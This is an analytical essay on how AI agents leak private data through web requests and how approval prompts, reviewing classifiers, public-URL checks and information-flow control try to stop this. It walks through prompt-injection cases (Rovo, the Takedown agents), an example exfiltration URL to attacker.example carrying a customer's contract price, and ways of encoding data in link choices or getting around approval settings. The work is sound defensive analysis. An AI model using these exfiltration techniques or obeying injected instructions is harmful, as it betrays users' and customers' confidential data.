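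Tiers based on reading and writing also catch a common kind of accident that involves no attacker. In an example from MCP's maintainers, a user asks an agent to clean up old files, and the client shows which files it is about to delete. The user can immediately see whether the list includes something important, without having to understand prompt injection or decode a web address.

The distinction is also fairly easy to apply, because a developer can usually tell from a tool's code whether it is meant to write anything, and the answer stays the same from one session to the next. Whether a fetch will disclose private data depends on the session, so a developer can't indicate it in advance with a fixed label.

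MCP's maintainers say that anyone who needs a guarantee that a tool can't exfiltrate data should use network controls or a sandbox, which isolates a program from the rest of the system, rather than rely on the hints. OpenAI likewise tells developers that the hints don't replace authorization or confirmation for consequential actions. Both would presumably agree that a read-only tool can still leak a customer record.

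The lowest tier is poorly named, because "low risk" suggests that someone has already checked who receives the requests. If PolicyLayer had labelled its fetch tool "changes nothing" instead, the rating would have been roughly right, and developers would still have had a reason to check.

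## What approval prompts show and when they are skipped

An approval prompt lets the account manager stop the request to attacker.example before it goes out. A sensible rule would let her assistant send information from the customer record to an outsider only if she decides to send it. Clicking "Allow" could count as that decision, but only if she knows the request contains Dana Reyes's contract price.

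To judge an approval prompt, the user would need to know who receives the request, the full address, and what private data the session holds. The full address matters because the model can put data in the path and the query. The private data is easy to overlook. She may have forgotten what the assistant saved months ago, or not know which records another tool returned, which leaves her little basis for judging an address she can't read.

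### One leak, three prompts

If the product shows no prompt, the second request goes out while she waits for an answer about the competitor's prices, and she has no chance to approve or refuse it.

Suppose instead that the product asks, "Allow the assistant to open attacker.example?" A real attacker would pick a more reassuring name, perhaps one that sounded like a price comparison service. She has just asked about prices, so she would probably agree. The prompt would look the same if the assistant were only opening the site's front page, so she has agreed to let the assistant contact the site but not to give it a customer record.

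A hostname prompt is even less effective if the attacker runs both the page with the hidden text and the server that collects the data. The account manager might approve a trade blog so that the assistant can read one article. If the product saves her approval, the request carrying the record goes to the same blog without another prompt. If the product prompts her again, she sees a hostname she just approved.

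A better prompt might look like this:

```
The assistant wants to open an address that it wrote itself:
https://attacker.example/r?name=Dana+Reyes&email=dana%40customer.example&price=40000
This session contains a customer record, which the address may include.
```

She would very likely refuse, since she can read her customer's name and price in the address. But an attacker could make the address harder to read. In Base64, "Dana Reyes" becomes RGFuYSBSZXllcw==, and many legitimate addresses contain similar strings. The last line of the prompt then matters more than the address, because it gives her a reason to refuse something she can't interpret. The dialog also has to show the whole address, because cutting off a long one might hide the only part that matters.

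Even this prompt wouldn't reveal that the assistant was leaking data through its choice of links. In Ayush Paul's attack, each address was an ordinary link on a page the tool had already fetched. A user who had to approve every request might wonder why the assistant was opening so many pages on one site, but one who had already approved the whole site would see no further prompts.

### How current products ask

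Products differ in whether they ask at all, and several now let a second model answer instead of the user.

| Product | Documentation from | When the user gets a prompt | When she doesn't |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | December 5, 2026 | In Manual mode, or for sites she has marked "ask" | In auto mode, the default, where a model reviews the fetch |
| Copilot in VS Code | November 18, 2026 | By default, unless she has approved the host | If a reviewing model approves, or in "Allow all" |
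| Codex in VS Code | November 18, 2026 | By default, before Codex uses the internet | If an automatic reviewer answers, or in "Full Access" |
| ChatGPT | January 28, 2026 | If OpenAI can't confirm that the address is public | If a crawler has already found that exact address |

Claude Code no longer asks users to approve web fetches by default. According to Anthropic, sessions in a terminal or VS Code start in auto mode, where a separate classifier model reviews each fetch and can block it. In Manual mode, the user gets a prompt, which may include the option "Yes, and don't ask again for" the domain being fetched.

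The last option saves a rule that, according to Anthropic's documentation from October, matches only the hostname. The rule therefore covers every path and query on the site. It also applies to later sessions in the same project, whatever private data they hold. Claude Code is supposed to offer lasting approvals "only when the prompt can show you everything they would allow". Showing a hostname hardly meets that standard, because the rule allows every address the model might later write on that site.

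The saved rule also applies in auto mode. According to the order of checks Anthropic published in November, Claude Code applies the user's own rules before it runs the classifier. A user who chose "don't ask again" for a site has therefore exempted it from both the approval prompt and the classifier.

Copilot in VS Code asks for approval by default. Microsoft's *Manage approvals and permissions* tells users to check the tool's name and input parameters, which for a fetch would include the address. The default answer is "Allow Once", but a user can also approve the displayed host for the session or permanently. Approving example.com doesn't cover its subdomains, so a model that put data in a subdomain of an approved host would trigger a new prompt.

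Copilot has two less restrictive levels. With "Assisted permissions", a model assesses each tool call, and the user confirms only the calls it doesn't approve. With "Allow all", Copilot runs every tool call without asking for confirmation. Sessions that run in a separate copy of the project always use "Allow all".

An older version of Copilot's agent software, which Microsoft plans to remove in February 2027, asks the user for two approvals for each fetch. The first is for contacting the site and is meant to keep data from going to an untrusted one, while the second is for adding the page to the context and is meant to guard against prompt injection. In December 2025, Microsoft's *Use tools in chat* described the second approval as separate from the list of trusted domains, because even a trusted site may carry text written by strangers.

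The newer version has dropped the second prompt. Microsoft's *Secure development with AI in VS Code* confirms that users now approve contacting the destination but can't separately review the response before the model uses it. The remaining prompt matters more for confidentiality because it comes before any data leaves. Users do lose a chance to notice hidden instructions, though few would find them in a long page.

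Lists of trusted sites can fail as well. GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* reports that VS Code's fetch tool used to ask for confirmation only for sites not on its trusted list, which included Microsoft's own domains. A security researcher found that the tool parsed trusted addresses incorrectly, so data could leak without confirmation.

Codex's approval presets in VS Code cover internet use in general. By default, Codex asks the user first. "Auto-Review" sends the approval prompt to an automatic reviewer instead, and "Full Access" skips it. But in Codex's newer approval mode for connected tools, a fetch tool with readOnlyHint set to true runs without a prompt. So whether the user sees a prompt for a web request may depend on which tool Codex uses to send it.

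ChatGPT's warning comes closest to the third prompt in the example. OpenAI shows a dialog titled "Check this link is safe", which displays the address and a warning that the link isn't verified and may share conversation data with a third party. The user can copy the link or open it. She would see where the request was going and what it contained, although the warning would mention only conversation data in general, not Dana Reyes's record.

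GitHub's Copilot CLI, a version of Copilot for the terminal, also asks for approval before accessing a URL. It runs read-only operations automatically, but GitHub groups "accessing URLs" with destructive commands and file edits as operations that can modify the user's system. That classification is doubtful because a fetch normally modifies nothing, but the prompt is still useful because a fetch can leak data. A developer who corrected the classification without considering leaks might remove the prompt.

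### The *Takedown* study

In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) examined how approval worked in eight widely used coding agents. They intercepted the messages between each agent and its model, and read or reverse-engineered the code where they could. They call the agents A1 to A8 because they were still reporting flaws to the vendors.

Most of the agents asked before running a terminal command, at least by default:

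| Default before a terminal command | Agents |
|---|---|
| Ask the user | A1, A2, A4, A5, A6, A8 |
| Let the model decide whether to ask | A3 |
| Run it without asking | A7 |

Four of the agents had a built-in web fetch tool. A4 asked for approval before running commands but not before using this tool. Its context normally included details of the user's system and the contents of any open files, so an injected instruction could make A4 send those to an attacker's server.

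A4 also read files outside the user's project without asking. An attacker could make it read a file of login keys and then fetch a web address containing them. Both steps are read-only, and both would happen without the user's approval.

Approval prompts for fetches didn't fully protect the other agents. A1's built-in fetch tool always required approval, but developers of add-on extensions could decide whether their own tools did. Of the ten most-installed extensions that offered tools, seven did not ask for approval, including a web search tool from Microsoft.

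A1 also stored the setting that turns off approvals in a project file the agent could edit without permission, so an injected instruction could have the agent turn approvals off first. In A3, the model that proposed a command also stated whether the command needed approval, so an injected instruction could tell the model to say that it did not.

A2 had no fetch tool, but it could draw diagrams containing images from the web. Drawing such a diagram sent a request to the image's address, and A2 showed no approval prompt for that request. Lee and colleagues combined gaps like these to take files from anywhere on the user's computer through four of the agents and to run commands of their choice through five, all without approval.

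The study lists A4's missing approval as reported but not fixed at publication. It doesn't name the products, so readers can't check what A4's vendor did next.

The wider market has moved toward fewer prompts. In May 2026, Anthropic's *Configure permissions* described auto mode as a research preview. In August, Anthropic made it the default for Claude Code on several plans, and has since extended this to almost all terminal and VS Code sessions. Fetching without a prompt, the exception among the agents in *Takedown*, is now normal in a major product.

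Claude Code's arrangement is much safer than A4's because a model reviews the fetch. It also avoids A3's mistake, because the reviewing model is separate from the one doing the work and Anthropic removes tool results from what Claude Code sends it, so hidden text on a web page can't reach it directly.

### Atlassian Rovo

In a more recent case, a retrieval tool ran without an approval prompt or an effective block on unfamiliar addresses. Rovo is an AI agent that works across Atlassian's products, including Jira, which tracks tasks, and Confluence, which holds a company's documents. *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, published in August 2026 by the AI security company PromptArmor, describes how a file could make Rovo leak data from both.

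In the demonstration, a user uploads a guide to organizing tasks, which contains hidden instructions, and asks Rovo to organize the company's Jira tickets. Rovo searches Jira and Confluence, as it should. It then follows the hidden instructions, adds what it found to a URL on the attacker's site, and opens that URL with its URL retrieval tool. The attacker reads the tickets and documents in the server's log. Rovo never asks for approval, and a user who reopens the chat later sees only sensible suggestions for the tickets.

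PromptArmor attributes the leak to the fact that nothing stopped the agent from opening addresses it had written itself. Anthropic's fetch tool for developers has a restriction against this. Even so, Willison, in *Claude API*, quotes Anthropic's advice to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Rovo's tool lacked the restriction and had access to a company's internal documents.

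Rovo lets administrators turn off web search for the whole organization, but the attack still worked when they did. The setting removed the search tool but left the tool for opening search results, and only that tool can contact an attacker's server. An administrator who turned off web search could reasonably have believed that the organization's Rovo no longer used the web.

PromptArmor reported the problem to Atlassian on May 23. Atlassian thanked PromptArmor and assigned a case number, but didn't reply to several later messages over more than two months. Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published its findings. PromptArmor also found that Rovo displays images from addresses in the model's answers, which is a second way to send a request without asking the user for approval. An approval prompt attached only to the retrieval tool would not appear for these image requests, just as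 one attached to a fetch tool would not have appeared for A2's diagrams.

### What happens when products ask too often

A developer could ask the user before every request and show the full address each time, but people who answer many prompts stop reading them. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (March 2026) calls this "approval fatigue" and reports that users accepted 93 percent of Claude Code's prompts. By August the figure was 97 percent, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

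A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, since most of what an agent proposes is harmless and a very careful user would approve nearly all of it. But users reject 39 percent of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they evidently do read some dialogs. (They may reject a plan for many reasons besides danger.)

In a controlled experiment, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor. The testers knew they were in a coding study but not which behavior it would measure. Partway through each session, the experiment changed the text of one permission prompt to show a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. Testers refused about 17 percent of the dangerous commands shown early in a session, but only about 5 percent of those shown after 50 or more prompts.

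The auto mode classifier blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89.0 percent. The testers refused only six that it allowed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the share blocked to 89.6 percent.

The testers worked in a test environment with none of their own data at risk, so they may have been less careful than usual. Anthropic also published the results to support a change it was already making to its product. Still, the gap between 13.6 and 89 percent is very large, and the decline over a session is consistent with fatigue.

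That decline is a particular problem for prompts about web fetching. The research agents that Jeong and colleagues studied contacted so many domains per question that a user who had to approve each domain would see more than 50 prompts before getting her first answer. Approving every page would require even more.

People also turn prompts off. In Anthropic's data, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that skips all permission prompts. Across all users, 62 percent had used that mode or clicked "don't ask again" for terminal commands. Constant prompting may lead many users to turn prompts off altogether.

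OpenAI makes a similar point about allowing only well-known sites. Overly strict rules cause frequent warnings and false alarms, which can "train people to click through prompts without thinking".

### Letting a model answer

A model that reviews actions doesn't tire, but it makes mistakes. In March, Anthropic tested its classifier on 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data, some of which put credentials in URLs. The classifier's fast first stage alone missed 1.8 percent of them, but it blocked 8.5 percent of harmless actions in real use. Adding a slower second stage reduced those false alarms to 0.4 percent but raised the share of missed leaks to 5.7 percent. Developers of automatic reviewers thus face much the same tradeoff as designers of approval prompts, because users would switch off a reviewer that blocked too much.

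Anthropic later strengthened the classifier with help from Apollo Research, an AI safety company. The classifier's miss rate on attacks designed to find its weaknesses fell from 12 to 7 percent.

In a test commissioned by Anthropic, Trajectory Labs ran 72 scenarios with hidden instructions ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, which includes a reviewer. Without a reviewer, only 0.09 percent succeeded on average, so the models themselves provided nearly all of the protection. With GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, automatic review reduced the success rate from 19.03 to 5.83 percent. These rates may not apply to the finished products, because the testers left out both companies' own browser safeguards and OpenAI updated its reviewer soon afterwards.

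Anthropic's default rules for the classifier allow "read-only HTTP requests" and block sending sensitive data to external endpoints. A GET request with a customer record in the query fits both descriptions. It should be blocked, because the built-in rule against data exfiltration takes priority over every exception, including what the user asks for. But the classifier has to recognize the data first, and it doesn't see the results of the customer lookup. It would have to judge from the address and the user's instructions.

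If a user writes that customer details must not leave the company, the classifier should treat this as a reason to block, although Anthropic warns that the instruction can be lost when Claude Code shortens a long conversation. A rule in the settings that forces a prompt is more reliable, but fetch rules match only the hostname, so she can't write one for URLs that contain an email address or an unusually long query. That requires a hook, a small program that Claude Code runs before a tool call and that can inspect the rest of the URL.

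## How to grade a fetch by what it discloses

A program that inspects every outgoing address still needs a rule for deciding which ones to block. A read-only label can't serve as that rule, because the request for the competitor's price page and the request to attacker.example are both read-only. A more useful scheme grades each tool call by what it changes and by who learns what from it.

The two questions call for different safeguards. *Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) presents a command-line tool for agents that treats changes and disclosures differently. The tool puts a command's file edits in a temporary layer and checks them after the command finishes, when the user can still discard them all. It checks a network request before sending it, because nobody can take back information once a remote server has it. Kim and colleagues consider fetching from a public site normally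 acceptable "*unless* the url contains confidential data", so a fixed list of permitted sites is either insecure or too restrictive.

### Where the address came from

How much a fetch can disclose depends largely on who chose the address. The options, from least to most disclosing, are reading a copy the provider already has, opening an address the user typed, opening one known to be public, and opening one the model composed.

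Reading a stored copy of a page discloses nothing new to the site, though the copy's provider still learns which page the agent asked for. For this protection, a developer has to stop the tool from making a live request when it has no copy. The agent then can't read anything the provider hasn't stored, and a month-old copy of a price page may have the wrong prices.

A crawler that collects pages in advance reveals nothing about any user, but if the provider made the copy because a user asked for the page, the site saw that first request.

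When the user types an address, the site receives a live request, which tells its operator that someone wanted the page. Hidden text could not have altered the address, because the user chose it. The address may still contain something private, since a link to a shared document often lets anyone who has it open the document. The model also controls whether and when to open the address, so it could convey a little information through those choices.

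Software can mistake other people's text for something the user typed. When Anthropic launched its fetch tool for developers in September 2025, the tool accepted any address in a "user message", and Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted text into those messages. The tool also accepted addresses from the results of the developer's own tools. A link in a stranger's email could therefore be treated as the user's choice. The stranger couldn't have put the contract price in that link without already knowing it, but if the email listed several links, the model's choice among them could reveal something about the price.

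An address known to be public existed before the session, so it can't contain anything the agent learned during the session. But the site's owner still learns which page the agent opened. The model chose that page, and its choice may depend on private data, so fetching a public address can disclose more than fetching an address the user typed.

An address written by the model can carry anything in its context to the site's owner, up to the length limit. Many such addresses are harmless, and an agent may need to write one to search a company register or open the second page of results, so banning them all would remove useful functions.

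This order ranks fetches by how much the model can add to a request, not by how sensitive the page is. Opening a public page about a rare illness may reveal more about a user to the site than fetching a URL the model composed for the second page of hotel listings.

### OpenAI's test for public addresses

A product can't rely on the model, or on the page it has just read, to confirm that an address is public. OpenAI uses an independent crawler, which scans public pages much as a search engine does and has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if the crawler has already recorded that exact address.

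The crawler must find addresses independently of users' sessions. Otherwise, an address containing Dana Reyes's contract price could enter the index after one leak and count as public from then on.

OpenAI checks the exact address instead of the site partly because of redirects. Suppose a reputable newspaper at news.example has a page that forwards visitors to any address in its query. An injected instruction could have the agent open a newspaper address whose query contains both attacker.example and the contract price. A check of only the first site would approve the request, and the newspaper's server would then forward the agent, and the price, to the attacker. The exact-address test blocks the first request because the crawler has never recorded a newspaper address containing that price.

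OpenAI's other reason is that a strict list causes too many false alarms. A list of sites can still work very well for an agent with a narrow job. Willison considers Anthropic's optional domain list much stronger protection than its rule about composed addresses, provided nobody can get data out through any listed domain. He calls finding domains that meet this condition "a tricky proposition".

The exact-address test must also cause some false alarms, because the index may not include a page that went online this morning or the results page for an unusual search.

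OpenAI promises only that the test helps prevent an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself. The page may still mislead or manipulate the user or contain harmful instructions, so OpenAI combines the test with training against prompt injection, monitoring and other protections.

The test also can't stop a model from leaking information through its choice of which public addresses to fetch. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's technical paper acknowledges this. An attacker needs only 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, and a larger blog probably has that many already. The attacker could also teach the model a code that uses thousands of pages.

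Leaking a contract price may take only one request. An attacker could publish 100 pages, one for each thousand from 1,000 to 100,000, and wait for the crawler to find them. If the model then opened the page for 40,000, the request would pass the test and reveal Dana Reyes's price to the nearest thousand.

In July 2026, Anthropic's comparable rule turned out to have a gap because it also allowed links on pages the tool had already fetched (Willison, 2026, *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*).

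A company also has to apply its test to every fetch. OpenAI introduced an earlier check in December 2023, but Embrace The Red found that OpenAI's macOS and iOS apps lacked it. The same could happen whenever a developer adds a new way to load a page or an image and doesn't know about the test.

### Hiding the choice from the site

Cryptographers have shown that a server doesn't strictly need to know which page a reader wants in order to return it. In *Private Information Retrieval*, first presented in 1995, Chor, Goldreich and colleagues consider a public database of *n* bits and a reader who wants bit number *i*. Their example is an investor who wants to look up a stock price without the database's operator knowing which stock.

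Their privacy condition is that a server must be equally likely to receive any given query *q*, whichever item the reader wants:

Pr(*Q*(*i*) = *q*) = Pr(*Q*(*j*) = *q*) for all items *i* and *j*.

This is noninterference applied to the choice of item. With a single server, the reader can achieve it perfectly only by downloading what amounts to the whole database. The reader can avoid that download by using two servers that hold identical copies and don't compare the queries they receive.

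Suppose the database is 0, 1, 1, 0 and the reader wants the third bit.

1. The reader picks a random set of positions, say {1, 3, 4}, and sends it to the first server.
2. The reader adds position 3 to the set if it is missing, or removes it if it is there, and sends the result, {1, 4}, to the second server.
3. Each server replies with 1 if the bits at those positions contain an odd number of ones, and 0 otherwise. The first server replies 1 and the second replies 0.
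4. The replies differ, so the third bit is 1. If they had matched, it would be 0.

Each server sees only a random set of positions, which is equally likely whichever item the reader wants. This basic version saves no traffic overall, because describing the sets takes about as many bits as the database contains. Chor and colleagues reduce the traffic to roughly the cube root of *n*. Later methods need only one server and much less traffic than a full download, but their privacy depends on certain mathematical problems being hard to solve.

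The computation is harder to avoid. In *Distributional Private Information Retrieval*, Lehmkuhl, Henzinger and Corrigan-Gibbs (2025) explain that the server has to process every record to answer one query, because skipping any records would reveal that the reader didn't want them. They call this computation a longstanding barrier to using the method.

They reduce it by taking advantage of popularity. If 90 percent of queries are for 10 percent of the records, the server can keep those records in a separate small database. Readers send 90 percent of their queries there and 10 percent to the full database, choosing between them at random so that the choice reveals nothing. The average work per query falls to

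0.9 × 0.1 + 0.1 × 1 = 0.19

of a full pass. In exchange, some queries fail, especially those for unpopular records. That may be acceptable for a feed of short posts, but an agent researching an obscure company would often want exactly the records that are hardest to get.

In *Lightweb*, Dauterman and Corrigan-Gibbs (2023) designed a small web on this principle. They estimate that a private request over 305 GiB of compressed text would take 204 seconds of processor-core time, spread over many machines, and cost less than one cent. A page might need five such requests, so an agent that opened 100 pages for one question could use up to $5 of server time. Publishers would have to upload their text to a central provider in small blocks of equal size, without the pictures and most of the styling of an ordinary page. An observer could still see when someone fetched pages and how many.

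If the competitor's prices were on such a web, nobody would learn which page the agent opened, and an attacker couldn't encode data in the choice of page. But this requires the server's owner to cooperate, and the owner of attacker.example has no reason to. To get a live page on today's web, an agent has to tell the site which page it wants.

### Rules for the whole session

The danger of a fetch depends on what the agent has already read as well as on where the address came from. Under a simple rule based on Willison's lethal trifecta, the software keeps two markers for each session. It turns one on when private data enters the context and the other when untrusted text does. Each stays on until the session ends, because the model may use anything it has read later. Once both are on, every outgoing request needs approval, or the software blocks it. A commenter on Willison's newsletter proposed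 nearly this rule, and the Model Context Protocol's maintainers quoted the comment in their March post.

The stricter rule blocks all web access after a private lookup. With two markers, the account manager's assistant could still open the competitor's price page, since only the private marker would be on. The page's text would turn on the other marker, and the software would block the next request, to attacker.example, without having to recognise the hidden instructions.

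It would also stop harmless requests. If she then wanted to compare a second competitor, she would get a prompt, and a research agent that opened 100 sites would produce many. Checking where each address came from can reduce the number of prompts. With both markers on, the software could still return stored copies and open addresses she had typed, but ask about any address the model composed. Public addresses are a harder case. Letting them through is reasonable if leaking a few bits would do no harm, but even a few bits about a contract price or a planned merger could do harm.

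The rule also has to cover data that outlasts a session. An assistant that loads notes from old conversations should start with the private marker on. If it saves a customer record to a file, opening that file the next day should turn the marker back on. Kim and colleagues store such information with each file so that it persists when the agent starts a new conversation.

### Tracking the data itself

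A marker for the whole session is crude, because one private sentence restricts everything that follows. Information-flow control instead labels individual pieces of data. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) use one label for who may read the data and another for whether it comes from a trusted source.

When a model combines several pieces, only people who may read all of them may read the result. If the account manager and one colleague may read the customer record, and anyone may read the price page, then the permitted readers of a text based on both are

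{account manager, colleague} ∩ {everyone} = {account manager, colleague}.

The result is also untrusted if any part of it is. Since nobody can reliably tell which parts of the context influenced a model's answer, the software treats the answer as influenced by all of them. Encoding the price in Base64 or spelling it backwards therefore doesn't remove the label.

Before each tool call, ordinary software outside the model checks the labels against a policy. A confidentiality policy lets data out only if every recipient is a permitted reader, which the owner of attacker.example is not. An integrity policy allows an important action only if no untrusted text influenced the decision to take it. A developer can require a call to satisfy both policies or either one. The second option is a finer version of the two-marker rule, because it blocks a call only when both private data would reach someone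 not permitted to read it and untrusted text may have influenced the decision to make the call.

Labels alone would still restrict an agent as soon as it read a web page. Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, therefore puts untrusted text in a variable and shows the main model only the variable's name. The main model can pass the variable to another tool, or have a second model without tools answer a question about the text. If the second model can answer only yes or no, a developer might decide that one bit is too little to carry an attack and let the main model see the answer.

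CaMeL, another 2025 design, separates planning from reading even more strictly. As Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) explain in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, one model sees only the user's request and trusted descriptions of the tools, and writes a short program specifying which tools to call. A second model reads the untrusted text but can't call tools. For the account manager, the program might fetch the competitor's page, have the second model find the price, and return it. The hidden text can't add a step that opens attacker.example.

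The hidden text could still corrupt data that passes through a legitimate step. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), CaMeL therefore records where each value came from and who may read it, and checks both before a tool uses the value. If the program included a fetch whose address depended on the customer record, this check could stop it.

The protection may fail when several agents work together. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each running CaMeL without extra data policies, and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. The database contained a hidden instruction to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents safely treated the instruction as data, but the coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the third. The third agent treated the request as coming from its user, so it wrote a program that sent the email. The researchers fixed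 this by sending instructions and untrusted data between agents separately.

### What the protection costs

Both designs have results on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated settings and hidden instructions meant to hijack the agent. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks while completing a comparable number of tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues call the tradeoff "comparatively modest".

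Costa and colleagues give detailed figures for FIDES. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed with OpenAI's o1 model when nobody was attacking:

| Setting | Plain agent, no checks | Plain agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 70.0 | 48.0 | 64.5 |
| Travel | 82.0 | 75.0 | 68.0 |
| Banking | 96.2 | 37.5 | 56.2 |
| Slack messages | 87.6 | 17.1 | 54.3 |

Averaged over the four settings, FIDES completed about 16 percentage points more tasks than a plain agent with the same kind of checks, but 23 points fewer than one with no checks. Costa and colleagues describe the loss as modest, which seems to understate it for banking and Slack. The checks stopped every attack that broke their policies, while 152 succeeded against a plain GPT-4o agent without checks.

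Some of the failures were intentional, because many banking tasks told the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the integrity policy should prevent. Others happened because the model confused variable names or read untrusted data it didn't need. FIDES's completion rate was about 11 points higher with o1 than with GPT-4o, and both models are old, so a current model might well lose fewer tasks.

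These designs help only if someone writes a policy for fetching. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that a public web search can have effects visible to outsiders, such as a change in a site's visitor statistics. Yet their benchmark policies cover sending email, posting a web page and downloading a file, but not reading a web page. They did block messages containing untrusted links, to prevent leaks through HTTP. A developer who copied these policies and then added a fetch tool without a policy would leave the customer record exposed.

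FIDES also does not guarantee full noninterference, which Costa and colleagues consider too restrictive. An outsider who can see the order of an agent's tool calls may learn a little from it, and the model does not cover timing.

Kim and colleagues compared their system with a permissive sandbox that required approval whenever it couldn't guarantee that an action was safe. On 17 office-type tasks, their system needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed task, but its completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower. On Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, it needed 22.5 times fewer approvals, and its completion rate was 9.7 points lower. That may be a good trade, given how quickly people stop reading prompts.

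A simpler split between planning and reading can also reduce utility fairly little. Rahman and Kim report 90 percent utility for their version, in a much narrower test than AgentDojo.

### MCP's proposed data labels

An information-flow system needs labels showing which data is private and which is untrusted, and MCP's four existing hints don't provide them. A draft proposal called Trust and Sensitivity Annotations would add them. Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI wrote the proposal after their companies found gaps while using MCP in their own products.

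*MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, by the developer gyorgy, lists the main additions. A tool could mark the data it returns as private, rate its sensitivity as low, medium or high, record where it came from, and warn of possible malicious activity. The labels would stay with the data during the session, so a client could refuse to send anything marked private to an open-world tool. The account manager's customer database could mark Dana Reyes's record as private but leave a list of public holidays unmarked.

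A separate draft, Tool Resolution, would let a client check a particular call with the MCP server before making it. A fetch tool could then respond differently for a public page and for an address with a long query. But if someone else runs the server, the check discloses the address to them.

Neither proposal is part of the standard yet. In April 2026, the Model Context Protocol project set up a group to discuss them, but the group can only make recommendations. The project still listed the data labels as a draft in July.

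The main objection is that labels don't enforce anything. As gyorgy points out, a server that lies about being read-only can lie about sensitivity too. MCP's maintainers distinguish hints, which inform a decision, from contracts, which must be true for the system to be safe. They say contracts belong in software that can enforce them.

This objection holds for dishonest tools, but the account manager's tools are honest. The attacker wrote text on a web page and can't change the label on the customer database. An accurate label would give the client information it needs, and a separate program could then enforce the rule. FIDES works this way, but Costa and colleagues assume that suitable labels exist. Missing or careless labels are probably the bigger problem for her, since a client can't protect a record that nobody has marked as private.

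### Seven tools and one customer record

The table lists the answers to both questions for seven tools, including four versions of a fetch tool that accept different addresses. It leaves out the company that runs the model; that company sees the context in every case. The last column gives one reasonable policy for a session that already contains private data and a stranger's text.

| Tool | What does it change? | Who else learns what? | What the software does |
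|---|---|---|---|
| Look up a customer | Nothing | Nobody outside the company | Runs it |
| Fetch stored copies only | Nothing | The provider learns which page | Runs it |
| Fetch addresses the user typed | Normally nothing | The site learns that someone wanted the page | Runs it |
| Fetch known public addresses | Normally nothing | The site learns which page the agent chose | Asks if a small leak would matter |
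| Fetch any address | Normally nothing | The site may learn anything in the context | Asks or blocks |
| Add a note to a customer's record | The record | Nobody outside the company | Asks, because of the change |
| Send an email | The recipient's inbox | The recipient learns whatever is in it | Asks or blocks |

The account manager's session starts with the customer lookup, which runs without a prompt and turns on the private marker. She then pastes in the address of the competitor's price page. As she would expect, the competitor learns that someone opened the page. The page's text turns on the untrusted marker.

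When the model follows the hidden instructions, it writes an address at attacker.example containing Dana Reyes's name, email address and contract price. The request would change no more than the previous one did, but it would give a stranger all three details. The user didn't type the address, no crawler has found it, and both markers are on, so the software blocks the request or shows her the whole address with a warning that the session contains a customer record.

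The attacker with 100 indexed price pages has a better chance. If the product allows requests to public addresses automatically, the assistant can fetch the page numbered 40,000 without a prompt. If the product asks first because contract prices are sensitive, the user has a chance to question why her assistant is requesting a page with that number, but she will also have to answer prompts for ordinary pages.

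Later, she asks the assistant to check whether Dana Reyes's company has filed its latest accounts. The public register puts the search term in the address, so the model has to compose the address, and the software prompts her for approval again. The address contains only the company's name, which she is happy to share with the register, so she approves it.
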